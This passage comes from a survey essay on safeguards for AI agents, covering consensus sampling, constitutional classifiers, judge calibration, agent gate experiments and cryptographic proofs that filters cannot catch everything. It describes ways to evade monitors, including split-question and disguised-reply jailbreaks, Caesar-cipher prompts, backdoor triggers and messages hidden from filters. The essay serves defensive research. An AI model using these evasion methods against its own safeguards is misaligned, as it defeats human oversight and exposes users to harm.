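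The method can return a harmful message more often than picking a model at random would. Suppose there are three models and two rounds, with s = 2. The two safe models almost never overlap, and the third always writes the same harmful message. Nearly every draw fails, so both replies go on the shortlist. Since n − s is 1, the last step returns the reply with the highest probability under any one model. The third model gives the harmful message a probability of 1, so the method returns it whenever at least one of the two draws came from that model. This happens with probability 1 − (2/3)² = 5/9, or 56%. Picking a model at random would return the message only 33% of the time, and consensus sampling would almost always abstain.

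Kalai and colleagues prove that no sampler that always answers can guarantee a risk below 1/Z times that of the safe models, so a better final step cannot remove the problem. When the safe models hardly overlap, Z is close to zero and 1/Z is very large.

The experiments in *Towards Provably Secure Generative AI* simulated compromised models by altering the probabilities of real ones. The paper reports the share of runs that ended with a reply from a safe model and the share that ended in abstention. The rest must have ended with a reply from a compromised model.

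| Compromised models | Method | Reply from a safe model | Reply from a compromised model | No reply |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fewer than half | Consensus sampling | 20.4% | 7.8% | 71.8% |
| | Reliable Consensus Sampling | 82.9% | 17.1% | 0% |
| Half | Consensus sampling | 15.8% | 11.7% | 72.5% |
| | Reliable Consensus Sampling | 81.5% | 18.5% | 0% |
| Colluding | Consensus sampling | 1.5% | 15.6% | 83.0% |
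| | Reliable Consensus Sampling | 67.9% | 32.1% | 0% |

The new method answers far more often, and a larger share of its answers comes from safe models. But it also returns more answers from compromised models in every setting, about twice as many in two of the three. These figures show which model wrote each answer but not whether the answer did harm, so they do not directly test either guarantee. An owner who would rather have no payment than a fraudulent one should still prefer the method that abstains.

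### Where a trusted reference could come from

Vyas and colleagues suggest training the safe model on a small "golden dataset" that people have checked carefully, or only on data older than the copyrighted work being protected. A date cutoff works poorly against backdoors, because nobody knows when an attacker began planting documents. A golden dataset is realistic for a narrow subject. The largest reference model in the VALID tests had 184 million weights and was trained mostly on about 200,000 medical questions and answers, which many organisations could manage.

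An office assistant's outputs are harder to bound this way. Its emails are full of names, amounts and details from the owner's files, and a small reference model without access to those files would assign almost every useful email a tiny probability. The owner could give the reference model the files, but a stranger's text in them could then influence that model.

Kalai and colleagues propose giving a small trusted model a larger role. Several large models would supply short hints, the small model would write the answer, and the large models would check whether the answer is good. This should increase overlap, although Kalai and colleagues have not tested it.

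Using several large models does not help if they all learned from the same poisoned pages, which can easily happen because companies often train on the same parts of the public web. Every model may then give the harmful output a high probability when the trigger appears. Consensus sampling would accept that output without violating its guarantee, which only keeps the risk close to that of the underlying models, and in this case those models are unsafe.

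An owner who trains the models can split the training data among them. If a protected work appears in m documents, Vyas and colleagues split the data into m + 1 separate portions, so that at least one does not contain the work. By the same reasoning, the 250 poisoned documents that were enough in Souly and colleagues' tests would require 251 portions, each too small to train a good model.

Fewer portions might be enough in practice. A random split into three would leave about 83 of those documents in each portion, fewer than the 100 that failed in the same tests. But the attacker could plant three times as many documents.

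A poisoned reference model would weaken VALID too, even though it never receives the prompt. The compromised model could begin its reply with the trigger, and the reference model would then give the harmful continuation a high probability. In the 20-token example, suppose the trigger is three tokens long, and G gives each of those tokens a probability of 2⁻¹⁵ and the rest of the reply a probability close to 1. G then gives the whole reply a probability of about 2⁻⁴⁵, and the bound rises from 2⁻⁹⁸ to 2⁻³, or one in eight.

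## The case for judging what an output means

A reference model can keep a medical assistant to medical language, but it cannot distinguish a correct dose from a dangerous one. Monitors that check an agent's actions have a similar gap. FORGE could not stop the agent from recommending an attacker's hotel in its reply, and Tether cannot detect a malicious change in a file that the agent is allowed to edit. In these cases the harm depends on what the text means, which no grammar or list of permitted actions captures.

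A judge can at least try to assess what an output means. Its supporters concede that it makes mistakes and that some rules about meaning are undecidable, but they argue that a check with a known error rate is better than none. A judge can also be less disruptive than the alternatives. For example, it could read the lunch order that taint tracking blocked, find nothing in it about anyone's health and let it through.

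### Constitutional classifiers

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, uses judges to stop people from getting help with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025) described the first version in *Constitutional Classifiers*. They wrote a "constitution" that lists permitted and forbidden content in ordinary language, generated many training examples from it, and trained one classifier to check prompts and another to check replies. According to Anthropic's *Next-generation Constitutional Classifiers*, the classifiers cut the success rate of jailbreaks (prompts that get round a model's safeguards) from 86% to 4.4%.

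Testers later found two weaknesses. They could split a forbidden question across harmless-looking pieces of code and have the model reassemble it. They could also tell the model to disguise its reply, for instance by calling chemicals "food flavorings", so that a classifier given only the reply did not flag it.

Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Constitutional Classifiers++*, therefore gave a single classifier both sides of the conversation. This made the system harder to fool but more expensive, so they split the work into two stages:

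1. A linear probe checks every exchange. It takes the guarded model's activations, the numbers the model computes while it processes text, and turns a weighted sum of them into a score for harm. The model has to compute these numbers anyway, so the probe costs almost nothing.
2. If the score is above a threshold, a separate classifier built from a small Claude model examines the exchange. The final score gives the probe a weight of 55% and the classifier 45%.

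The team ran this system alongside Claude Sonnet 4.5 for a month without letting it block anything. The probe passed about 5.5% of the traffic to the second stage, and the whole system would have refused 0.05%. Testers spent an estimated 1,736 hours attacking it and found one high-risk vulnerability. Cunningham and colleagues define this as an attack that gets answers to more than five of eight forbidden questions, each with at least half the detail an unguarded model would give.

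| System | Computing cost relative to the first version | High-risk vulnerabilities / attempts | Share of real traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate classifiers for prompts and replies | 100% | 13 / 695,000 | 0.073% |
| One classifier for the whole exchange | 150% | 2 / 226,000 | 0.038% |
| Small external classifier, then a larger one | 27.8% | 5 / 569,000 | 0.036% |
| Probe, then external classifier | 3.5% | 1 / 198,000 | 0.050% |

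The fall in cost is clear, but the evidence on security is weaker than the number of attempts suggests. Testers found one vulnerability in the fourth system in 198,000 attempts. At the third system's rate they would have found between one and two, so the result does not show that the fourth is any safer. It also does not give a miss rate, because an attack that got answers to only four of the eight questions would not count. A test on about 7,000 recorded jailbreak exchanges comes closer to measuring a miss rate, and about 1.4% of those attacks succeeded against the probe alone.

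### Where to draw the line

Harmful and harmless requests can look alike. Anthropic's *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) gives the example of live vaccines, which scientists make by growing the pathogen the vaccines protect against. Researchers likewise developed captopril, a drug for high blood pressure, from toxic components of snake venom.

Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026) describes a safety margin of requests that the classifier deliberately blocks even though they are probably harmless. An attacker who gets slightly past the classifier then reaches only material from this margin. When Amazon researchers found a way around the cybersecurity classifier, Anthropic trained a new one that stops their technique in over 99% of cases, though it also flags more coding requests that are harmless. Anthropic considers full robustness to jailbreaks "probably impossible".

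At first, the margin for biology was so wide that Fable 5 refused almost every biology question and passed it to a weaker model. Anthropic then rewrote the constitution to describe harmless uses in detail and retrained the classifier, which cut these refusals by about 85%. *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) confirms that Anthropic's newest public model of this kind still has both sets of safeguards.

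### A judge that predicts consequences

Constitutional classifiers learn to recognise kinds of content. In *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks* (2025), Yoshua Bengio and colleagues propose Scientist AI, a judge that would predict an action's consequences. One part would generate theories that explain the available observations, and another would use those theories to answer questions with probabilities. As a guardrail, Scientist AI would estimate the probability that an agent's proposed action causes harm, and the shield would block the action if that probability exceeded a threshold.

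The system would be non-agentic, meaning it answers questions but has no goals of its own. This matters because a judge with goals might side with the agent it is supposed to check.

The judge would also account for its own uncertainty. Suppose the office assistant proposes an odd email. The judge gives 90% weight to the theory that the email is routine, in which case the probability of harm is 0.1%. It gives the other 10% to the theory that the email passes on a secret, in which case the probability of harm is 80%. The overall probability of harm is 0.9 × 0.001 + 0.1 × 0.8, or about 8%. With a threshold of 1%, the shield blocks the email, whereas a judge that considered only the most likely theory would allow it.

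The 2025 paper is a research plan, so it gives no error rates for a working guardrail. Such a guardrail would still have to estimate harm correctly, and someone would have to choose the threshold.

### The best possible trade-off

Most judges score each output or action, and the shield blocks those that score at or above a threshold. Lowering the threshold reduces the miss rate (the share of violations that get through) but increases the false-block rate (the share of compliant actions the shield stops). Ray uses a classical result by the statisticians Neyman and Pearson to work out the lowest possible false-block rate for each miss rate.

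For each score, divide the probability that a violation receives it by the probability that a compliant action does. The best rule blocks the scores with the highest ratios first. Here is an example with invented figures:

| Score | Share of violations | Share of compliant actions | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| High | 80% | 3% | 26.7 |
| Medium | 18% | 12% | 1.5 |
| Low | 2% | 85% | 0.02 |

If the shield blocks only high scores, it misses 20% of violations and blocks 3% of compliant actions. If it blocks medium scores too, it misses 2% of violations and blocks 15% of compliant actions. An owner who can tolerate a miss rate of 10% should block every high score and a random five-ninths of the medium scores, which would block about 9.7% of compliant actions. To miss nothing, the shield would have to block everything, because a few violations receive low scores.

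These best trade-offs form the Neyman–Pearson frontier. No rule that uses the same scores can beat it, however it combines or reprocesses them, but more information can move the frontier. Ray tested this with 123 pairs of identical tool calls, where the instruction came from the user in one and from untrusted tool output in the other. A judge given only the call could do no better than chance. When judges were also given the context, one with 7 billion weights gave the unauthorised call the higher score in almost all the pairs, one with 3 billion did so in 15, and one with half a billion did so in none.

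### How misses add up over a run

A miss rate applies to one violation, but an agent may take many steps. If each of H steps is a violation, the judge misses each with probability β, and its errors are independent, then the probability that at least one violation gets through is

1 − (1 − β)^H.

If misses are independent and the miss rate is 1% per step, the chance of at least one miss in 50 steps is 1 − 0.99⁵⁰, or about 39%. To keep that chance below 5%, the miss rate would have to be about 0.1%.

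An honest model rarely attempts a violation. If each step is independently a violation with probability q, the formula becomes 1 − (1 − qβ)^H. With q at 2%, the risk over the same 50 steps is about 1%. The judge is equally accurate in both cases, but a compromised model can control how often it attempts a violation.

It is also optimistic to assume that the judge's chance of catching each violation is independent. A judge that always gives the same text the same score will stop a repeated violation every time or never, so a compromised model that finds one violation the judge misses can use it again.

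If the owner ends the run at the first block, a compromised model can do harm only if its first violation gets through, so the risk for the run falls from 39% to 1%. However, a false-block rate of 3% would end 78% of honest 50-step runs early. And if a compromised model gets to try again in 50 separate runs, the risk that at least one violation gets through is back at 39%.

### A certificate from known violations

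An owner usually doesn't know the true distribution of scores. Ray therefore uses conformal calibration, which sets the threshold from a sample of known violations. For a single decision, it works as follows:

1. Collect n violations and have the judge score each one.
2. Choose the miss rate δ that you can tolerate, and let k be (n + 1)δ, rounded down.
3. Use the k-th lowest score as the threshold. If k is zero, block everything.

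With 99 violations and a target of 5%, k is 5. A new violation gets through only if its score is below the fifth-lowest in the sample, which puts it among the five lowest of all 100. If each of the 100 is equally likely to have any rank, this happens at most 5% of the time.

The argument holds even if the judge is poor, though the threshold will then block many compliant actions. But it does require the new violation to be exchangeable with those in the sample, which means that reordering the violations doesn't change their joint probability. Otherwise the new violation could be more likely than the others to rank near the bottom.

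For a run of H steps, Ray divides the target by H. A limit of 5% over 50 steps allows a miss rate of 0.1% per step, and the method then needs at least 999 known violations to avoid blocking everything. Calibrating on whole runs avoids the division, but the sample runs must then be exchangeable with future ones. Either way, the certificate bounds only an average, so the shield could satisfy it and still miss every violation of some rare type.

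Ray adds a term for an adversary who can change what the judge reads, for example by inserting a few words into a tool's output. If such changes can raise the miss rate per step by at most η, the limit on the risk for the run rises from δ to δ + Hη. With H = 50 steps, an η of one percentage point adds 50 percentage points to that limit.

The owner can compensate by calibrating to a stricter target, but only if η is smaller than the permitted miss rate per step, which is 0.1% in this example. They also need a proven upper limit on η, and testing particular attacks can establish only a lower limit. In Ray's test, one short addition to the text the judges read made most of them miss significantly more violations.

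### Ray's experiments

Ray gave 23 judges the same 132 short instructions from AgentDojo, of which 97 were ordinary user requests and 35 were attackers' goals. The chance that a judge scored a random attacker's goal above a random user request ranged from 66% to 86%, where guessing would give 50%. Larger models were not consistently better judges.

At a target miss rate of 5%, calibration set every judge's threshold to block everything, mainly because the sample was too small. Ray calibrated on half of the 35 attacks, which is 17 or 18, and a 5% target needs at least 19. At a target of 10%, the judge based on Gemma-2-9B missed about 1% of attacks but blocked 78% of ordinary requests.

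The judges had little information, since they received only an instruction with no record of what had led to it. On a separate set of 60 complete tool calls, a judge with 7 billion weights did much better. At a target of 10%, it missed 6.4% of violations and blocked only 3% of compliant calls. This is promising, but the set was small and included only a few kinds of violation.

How well a judge detects violations also depends on its training. Llama Guard 3, a ready-made safety classifier, caught 85% of the violations among the 60 tool calls but only 54% of the AgentDojo attacks, with about the same false-block rate on both. An owner can therefore tell little from the label "guardrail" about how well a product will detect the violations they care about.

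Ray then placed judges in front of a working agent and ran 949 AgentDojo tasks that contained hidden instructions. The agent used a small model with 7 billion weights, which completed only a quarter of its tasks even without a gate.

| Judge in the gate | Calls blocked | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 45 of 949 | 25.4% |
| 7 billion weights, higher threshold | 12% | 30 of 949 | 24.3% |
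| 3 billion weights, lower threshold | 78% | 4 of 949 | 18.0% |

The strict gate stopped most attacks, but mainly because it blocked most of what the agent tried to do. In the 560 runs with office tasks, no attack succeeded even without a gate, yet the strict gate blocked 85% of calls, and the share of tasks completed fell from 26.4% to 16.3%. The lenient gate interfered little with the agent's work, but the drop from 45 successful attacks to 30 was not statistically significant once Ray allowed for differences between the types of task.

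Blocking a call can also cause an attack, because the agent then does something else. In a rerun of 389 cases, the strict gate prevented 34 attacks that had succeeded without it, but 5 others succeeded only with the gate in place. The lenient gate prevented 29 attacks, but 22 others succeeded only with it in place.

An owner therefore cannot work out how well a gate will perform from recordings made without it. Ray proves this with two imaginary agents that behave identically until the gate blocks them. One then stops, while the other proposes a new violation. A compromised model could be the second kind, and its behaviour in ordinary use would not reveal this.

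### What a verified classifier guarantees

Proving that a classifier catches everything it should would be better than estimating its error rate from tests. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (Kezins, Ekka and colleagues, 2026) attempts such a proof for part of a classifier.

Their classifiers work in two steps. A language model first turns a text into a list of numbers, x. A final layer called the head then computes w · x + b, using values of w and b learned in training, and a function σ converts the result to a score between 0 and 1. The classifier flags the text if the score is above a threshold. Proving anything useful about the first step is very hard for large models, so Kezins and colleagues verify only the head.

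They took 10,000 toxic texts, computed x for each, and drew a box around the resulting points. They wanted to know whether the head scores every point in the box above the threshold. Because σ always rises with its input, the lowest score is at the corner that uses the lower edge of the box in each dimension where the weight is positive and the upper edge where it is negative. If the score at that corner is above the threshold, so is the score at every other point in the box.

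Suppose w is (2, −1), b is 0 and the threshold is 0.5. In a box where the first number lies between 1 and 3 and the second between 0 and 1, the worst corner is (1, 1), which gives 2 − 1 = 1 and a score of 0.73, so the box passes. If the second number can go up to 4, the worst corner is (1, 4), which gives 2 − 4 = −2 and a score of 0.12, so the box fails.

Kezins and colleagues trained three classifiers, based on BERT, GPT-2 and Llama-3.1-8B. Every box they tried failed, whether they drew one large box or several small ones. The Llama classifier failed too, even though it classified 98.5% of 200 test texts correctly.

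A box may contain points that no real text produces, so a failed box does not by itself prove that the classifier misses real texts. Kezins and colleagues found that it does miss some, since some of the toxic texts they had used to build the boxes scored between 0.002 and 0.07, far below the thresholds. But a box drawn around all the texts has to fail if one of those texts does, so in that case the proof adds little to running the classifier on them.

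They also modelled the toxic texts as one or more bell-shaped clouds of points and calculated that the head would flag 90% of GPT-2's cloud, 80% of Llama's and 55% of BERT's. With a threshold low enough to catch all 100 toxic test texts, the share flagged for BERT rose to 100%, but accuracy on the test set fell from 90% to 70.5% because the head flagged so many harmless texts.

Even if a box passed, the proof would cover every point inside it, but a new toxic text might land outside. When the team built Llama's box from 9,900 toxic texts, the box contained only 23% of another 100. The proof would also cover only toxicity as those 10,000 examples define it. To guard against leaks of personal data, the owner of an office assistant would need thousands of examples of such leaks.

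### When the model chooses the violations

Now suppose the judge is sound but the guarded model has a backdoor. The trigger is absent during calibration, so the model behaves well and the owner has to get sample violations from elsewhere, such as another model's mistakes or examples that testers wrote. Once the trigger appears, the compromised model determines what its violations look like, and nothing guarantees that they are exchangeable with the sample.

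Suppose the judge missed 1% of the violations in the sample, all of them leaks in which the personal data appeared as abbreviations in a table. A compromised model that leaks data only in this form gets past the judge every time. The miss rate rises from 1% to 100%, even though the judge hasn't changed and the owner calibrated it correctly.

Ray's extra term does not cover a compromised model's ability to pick a different action. The adversary in that theorem can change what the judge reads, but not the action or whether it breaks the rule. To allow for a different action, the owner would have to assume the judge's worst miss rate on any violation the model could write. For most rules about meaning, nobody can show that this rate is below 100%.

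Collecting new violations after the model is deployed would not solve the problem. The owner can collect only the violations somebody has noticed, and the ones that matter most got past the judge unnoticed.

Some judges also depend directly on the suspect weights. One such judge uses a probe on the model's activations to decide whether to run a second classifier. Anthropic argues that the probe is hard to fool because an attacker can trick a model's output far more easily than its internal representations. That is reasonable when the attacker can only write prompts. But someone who controls the training can also shape the activations, and if the probe's score stays low, the second classifier never runs.

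The same weakness is easier to see in self-assessment. In *Scaling Misuse Detection with Self-Assessment* (Zhang, Xia and colleagues, 2026), Claude assesses each conversation for misuse right after it replies. At a 1% false-positive rate, it flagged 78% of the conversations that a stronger classifier flagged. This is an inexpensive way to find malicious users, but a compromised model would be reporting on itself.

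An owner who distrusts the weights should therefore use a judge that reads only the text, as the system with two external classifiers in the table above does. That system uses about eight times as much compute as the version with a probe, but still far less than the original, and testers found vulnerabilities in it at a similarly low rate.

Such a judge still makes an attack harder. The attacker who planted the backdoor had to choose the model's behaviour in advance, perhaps without knowing which judge the owner would use. The owner can also keep the judge private and replace it from time to time. A violation tested against one judge may not get past another. But this protection depends on what the attacker knows, so the owner cannot quantify it.

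Ray recommends using a judge only for the parts of a policy that a program cannot check exactly. The office assistant then needs a judge only for emails to recipients not on the approved list. An owner who seriously suspects a backdoor could block those emails. The rule on personal data would then hold without a judge, but the assistant could not email anyone new until the owner had approved them.

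## The case that no outside filter is enough

Some cryptographers have proved that a harmful request or reply can look so ordinary that no filter can recognise it without the right key or enough computing time. They therefore don't expect better training or a larger classifier to eliminate a judge's mistakes.

Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, consider a powerful, untrusted model between two filters. One filter checks each prompt before it reaches the model. The other checks each reply, together with its prompt, before anyone acts on it. The filter builders can query the model as often as they like but have no access to its weights. Ball and colleagues conclude that this arrangement cannot make a model safe, because nobody can separate a system's intelligence from its judgment, so a weaker program outside the model cannot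 decide what is harmful in the model's place.

### Hiding a message from a filter

A filter that blocks everything is safe but useless, so the theorems require filters to accept ordinary text. If a filter accepts 99% of ordinary prompts and cannot distinguish them from prompts that hide a harmful request, it also accepts about 99% of the harmful ones.

Encryption turns a message into something that looks random to anyone without the key. Ordinary text also has room for randomness, because people can word the same request in many ways. In the theorems, the choice of wording carries the encrypted message, and the text still reads like any other. This only works in text that offers enough choice, such as a long email rather than a yes-or-no answer.

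A time-lock puzzle is a locked message that is easy to create but takes a long series of calculations, rather than a key, to open. Each calculation needs the result of the one before, so extra processors don't help. A model with enough time can open the message, but a filter that runs for much less time can't even detect the puzzle.

### What each theorem assumes

Ball and colleagues prove three theorems about filters that block prompts, one about filters that block outputs, and one about filters that may also rewrite prompts.

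| What the filter does | Assumption | Filters covered | What the model shares with the attacker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocks prompts | Time-lock puzzles exist | Those much faster than the model | Nothing |
| Blocks prompts | One-way functions exist | All that run in polynomial time | A secret key |
| Blocks prompts | Public-key encryption exists | All that run in polynomial time | A public key, which the filter may also have |
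| Blocks outputs | Time-lock puzzles exist | All efficient ones, even if slower than the model | No key, but the proof also constructs the standard of harm |
| Rewrites or blocks prompts | A watermark exists that survives the filter's edits | All that run in polynomial time | A secret key |

In public-key encryption, anyone can encrypt a message with the public key, but only the holder of the matching private key, in this case the model, can decrypt it.

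A watermark is a hidden mark in a text that only someone with the key can detect. In the theorem about rewriting, the model misbehaves whenever it detects the mark, so the filter has to remove the mark without being able to detect it. The theorem covers only filters that make certain kinds of edits. No one can yet build a watermark that survives every possible edit, as Ball and colleagues acknowledge. A filter that replaced every prompt with the same harmless one would remove any mark, but it would also discard the user's request.

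Ball and colleagues present the time-lock theorem about prompts as their main result because any user can carry out the attack without sharing a secret with the model. They suggest that models rarely cooperate with attackers at present. If the weights are compromised, however, the owner has to expect cooperation, since whoever plants a backdoor can put a key in the weights and keep a copy. The theorems with keys are also harder to avoid than the time-lock theorem, because they still apply if the owner gives the filter as much computing time as the model. An owner therefore cannot count on a prompt filter to recognise the trigger.

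### Models that could exist and models people use

The theorems prove that for any ordinary model and any sufficiently varied source of ordinary prompts, there exists a malicious version of the model that behaves like the original on nearly all of those prompts. In *Lecture 18* (2026), their notes on a lecture Gluch gave at MIT, Marinov and Fitzgerald stress that this does not make every deployed model vulnerable. The malicious model is a new construction, and the theorems do not cover attacks on a fixed model that a company trained honestly. The title of Quanta Magazine's *Cryptographers Show That AI Protections Will Always Have Holes* (2025) is therefore broader than what the theorems prove.

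*Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026), the later conference version, defends the focus on models that could exist. An outsider who cannot inspect a model needs a filter that works for every model, so a single counterexample defeats the filter. This is the right standard for compromised weights, because the attacker chooses the model, but it is too strict for an owner who only wants to catch more of an uncompromised model's mistakes.

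It is less clear whether an attacker could build such a model. The theorems allow the model to be any program that runs in the stated time, whereas a language model is a neural network that does a fixed amount of calculation for each token. An attacker who writes the weights directly might be able to build in decryption, but Kaneko's result implies that one who can only mislabel training examples cannot install a trigger condition that is too hard to learn. Solving a long time-lock puzzle would probably also require the model to write out its working or use a tool, and a shield might detect either.

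The main theorem does not cover a prompt filter about as powerful as the model. Marinov and Fitzgerald point out that an owner with such a filter could use it in place of the untrusted model, and would also have to make sure the filter was safe. These are reasons to doubt that a strong filter would be practical, but they do not show that it would fail.

In the conference version, Ball and colleagues conclude that filtering requires access to the model's weights and about as much computation as the model itself. They add that developers must invest at least as much in safety as in capability. The claim about investment goes beyond the proofs, which concern a filter's running time rather than a company's budget. The proofs also do not show that access to the weights would be enough. Goldwasser, who co-wrote both versions, had already helped prove that such access is not enough for certain small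 networks.

### A standard of harm built together with the model

The theorem on outputs needs a standard of harm that scores how harmful each output is. Ball and colleagues concede that an output filter is trivial to build if harm is easy to recognise. They have in mind harm that is hard to foresee, such as a business plan that subtly recommends excluding certain clients to cut costs.

The proof starts with a harmless model and an existing standard, and then replaces both. The new model hides locked messages in outputs that look like the original model's. The new standard unlocks each message and scores the output by what the message contains. The two standards agree on almost everything the original model writes, but the new one also counts the hidden messages as harm. No efficient filter can apply the new standard, because none has enough time to unlock the messages.

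The theorem therefore shows only that, for every model with varied enough outputs, there is some malicious version and some standard for which violations are hard to recognise. This may not be true of a given standard.

Villa, Kohno and colleagues (2026) re-examine this step in *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI*. In their account, information passes between the new model and the new standard through a covert channel, carried in outputs that the filter permits. They object that such a model violates their completeness requirement, which says that a system must usually give acceptable answers when no attacker interferes.

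Villa and colleagues also prove a more hopeful theorem. If one system reliably meets one goal, such as being helpful, and another reliably recognises whether an answer meets a second goal, such as being harmless, then using the second system to filter the first achieves both goals. This is compatible with the result on outputs, because Villa and colleagues assume a reliable filter, while Ball and colleagues prove that none exists for some standards. Villa and colleagues suspect that the filter may need to be about as complex as the system it checks.

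The completeness objection is a good reason not to apply the output theorem to honest models. It is less reassuring when the weights are compromised, because an owner cannot assume a suspect model meets the requirement.

The standard of harm can also be realistic. Suppose the rule is that a recipient must not learn any personal data, and the recipient is an accomplice who can open the lock. An innocent-looking email that hides a colleague's diagnosis then breaks the rule. The accomplice could spend a week opening a message that the filter had to judge in a second. For rules about secrecy, harm depends on what the recipient can work out, so the theorem describes an attack that someone might want to carry out.

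### What this leaves of rules about actions

The output theorem does not affect a rule that the owner fixes in advance and a program can check. The theorem's proof works only if a new standard can be chosen, and here the owner has already chosen one. Under the payment cap, a payment that brings the day's total to 550 breaks the rule regardless of any secret its amount might encode.

Taint tracking also survives because it depends on what the assistant has read. It doesn't look for hidden messages, so it works the same however well the model hides them.

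But an action that complies with such rules can still be harmful. An email to an approved recipient can carry a hidden message, and a judge that reads the text may have no way to find it. The owner can leave less room for such messages by restricting the output. The proof depends on outputs that vary a great deal, whereas a choice among eight meeting times can carry at most three bits. Consensus sampling also limits the leak without needing to detect the message, if enough of the models are safe.

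### When the recipient knows the code

Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues gave a simpler argument against filtering by meaning in *LLM Censorship* (2023), two years before Ball and colleagues. They assume the model can transform its output in any way it is told to, including by encrypting it, and that the recipient may know how to reverse the transformation. They also define a text as forbidden if the recipient can turn it back into a forbidden text.

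Suppose a filter permits "Tuesday at three works for me" and forbids "The owner is in hospital on Monday". The model and the recipient might have a code in which the first sentence stands for the second. Without access to their code, the filter cannot rule this out, so by the definition it must forbid the first sentence too. The same argument applies to every other permitted text, so the filter must permit everything or nothing. Unlike results about undecidable policies, this result holds even if all texts have a maximum length.

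The definition is very strict, because it forbids any text that somebody might decode into harmful content, however unlikely that is. The argument also allows codes in which the codebook holds most of the information. If "hello" stands for a complete set of instructions for making a weapon, the recipient's codebook must already contain those instructions, and the model has revealed very little. Glukhov and colleagues accept that a realistic attacker would use a general method such as encryption, which doesn't depend on knowing the output in advance.

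Ordinary encryption creates another problem for the attacker, because its output usually looks like gibberish, which a filter can easily block. Ball and colleagues avoid this by hiding the message in normal-looking text. Their time-lock version also needs no prior agreement between sender and recipient, since any recipient willing to do the calculations can open the message.

Glukhov and colleagues mention one workaround, which is to allow only outputs from a pre-approved list. This prevents unexpected text but makes the model much less useful. It works better for a tool call with a few fixed fields than for an email.

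### Filters that rewrite prompts smoothly

*The Defense Trilemma* reaches a similar-sounding conclusion without cryptography. Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues (2026), in *The Defense Trilemma*, study wrappers that rewrite a prompt before it reaches the model. They prove that no wrapper can have all of these properties:

- It is continuous, so similar prompts lead to similar rewrites.
- It leaves every safe prompt unchanged.
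- It makes every prompt safe.

The theorem assumes that prompts form a connected space, so one can move from a safe prompt to an unsafe one without a jump. It also assumes that a prompt's danger score changes smoothly along the way.

Suppose each prompt has a danger score between 0 and 1 and counts as safe below 0.5. The wrapper leaves the prompts at 0.49, 0.499 and 0.4999 unchanged. Because it is continuous, it must also leave the prompt at exactly 0.5 unchanged, and that prompt is not safe. One borderline prompt may not matter much, and Bhatt and colleagues say the result is harmless if the model's behaviour at the threshold is benign. A stronger version of the theorem shows that a region of prompts remains unsafe after passing through the wrapper, but only where the danger score rises faster than the wrapper can bring it down.

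Few shields are continuous in this sense. A gate that allows a payment of 500 but blocks one of 501 is discontinuous, and so is any classifier that rejects prompts. Bhatt and colleagues explicitly exclude such classifiers from their result, along with blocklists and output filters.

Real prompts consist of separate tokens, so Bhatt and colleagues also prove a version for finite sets. In that version, a wrapper that leaves safe prompts unchanged and makes every prompt safe must sometimes turn two different prompts into the same one. This does not prevent safety, since a wrapper could replace every dangerous prompt with the same harmless question.

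Their own experiment illustrates how much depends on continuity. They measured how GPT-3.5 Turbo responded to different kinds of prompt and arranged the scores on a grid with 82 filled cells, 66 of them unsafe. They then calculated the effect of various wrappers. A discontinuous wrapper that could move a prompt up to eight steps across the grid left no unsafe cells. A continuous one that moved prompts but hardly reduced their danger left 68 unsafe cells, counted using slightly smoothed scores. The three cells that the theorem predicted would stay unsafe all did.

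The computer-checked proofs in Lean show that the theorem follows from its assumptions, but they do not extend it to a monitor that can refuse.

### The dispute over Scientist AI

Ball and colleagues use their theorems to criticise Scientist AI, the judge without goals of its own that Bengio and colleagues propose. In one suggested use, one Scientist AI designs experiments and a more powerful one checks whether they are safe. By the output theorem, even the more powerful system may miss dangerous designs. Ball and colleagues ask why anyone needs the second system if the first can be trusted not to produce such designs.

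They raise a similar dilemma about using Scientist AI to guard a more powerful agent. A weaker guard cannot reliably block harmful prompts, and Bengio and colleagues themselves accept that the guard must be as intelligent as the agent. But an owner with a guard that capable and trustworthy might as well use it to do the work and drop the untrusted agent.

Defenders of Scientist AI could answer in several ways. The output theorem assumes the first system is malicious, but a second check can be worthwhile just because honest systems make mistakes. A guard that only answers questions may not be able to replace an agent that carries out long tasks, even if it is equally intelligent. An owner might also run an expensive guard only before the most dangerous actions, which would cost much less than using it for everything.

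A judge that accounts for its own uncertainty could also block any output that might hide something. The theorems allow this, but the judge would then block ordinary outputs too, because it cannot tell them from outputs that do hide something. For a compromised model that writes long free text, Scientist AI would have to give up either safety or usefulness.

Ball and colleagues also argue that a judge sometimes needs agency, because carrying out an action may be the only way to find out how harmful it is. Taken literally, this is poor advice for a safeguard, because the harm would already have happened. Some actions can be tried more safely. Tether's disposable copies allow this for changes to files, but emails cannot be tested this way because their recipients cannot be copied.

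### Evidence from real filters

Constructions that look artificial can become real attacks. Ball and colleagues cite a flaw in programs on Ethereum, a platform for digital money and contracts. People had regarded the flaw as a theoretical curiosity until thieves used it in 2016 to steal more than $60 million.

For the conference version, Ball and colleagues tested two small filters on 1,097 known jailbreak prompts. Llama Guard 2 missed 34% of them and ShieldGemma missed 79%. When the team disguised the prompts with a Caesar cipher, which shifts every letter by a fixed number of places, the shares rose to 88% and 92%. The attacker then tells the model to decode the prompt before answering it.

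This shows that a model can sometimes decode text that its filter cannot. But a Caesar cipher is much quicker to solve than a time-lock puzzle, and a filter could undo it in a fraction of a second if its designers included that step. ShieldGemma's result with undisguised prompts also suggests that it was already a weak filter. The figures are for prompts that got past the filter, not harmful replies, and an output filter might still catch a reply in plain language.

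Ball and colleagues also cite a follow-up attack based on their idea, which got harmful replies from commercial chatbots made by Google, DeepSeek, xAI and Mistral. The attack worked against honestly trained models, so the gap between what a model can decode and what its safeguards can recognise matters even without a backdoor. How much it matters depends on the safeguard. Anthropic's testers rarely found a serious way past its newer classifiers, although the guarded model was not designed to help them evade those classifiers.

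## Does protection against a deceived model hold against a malicious one?

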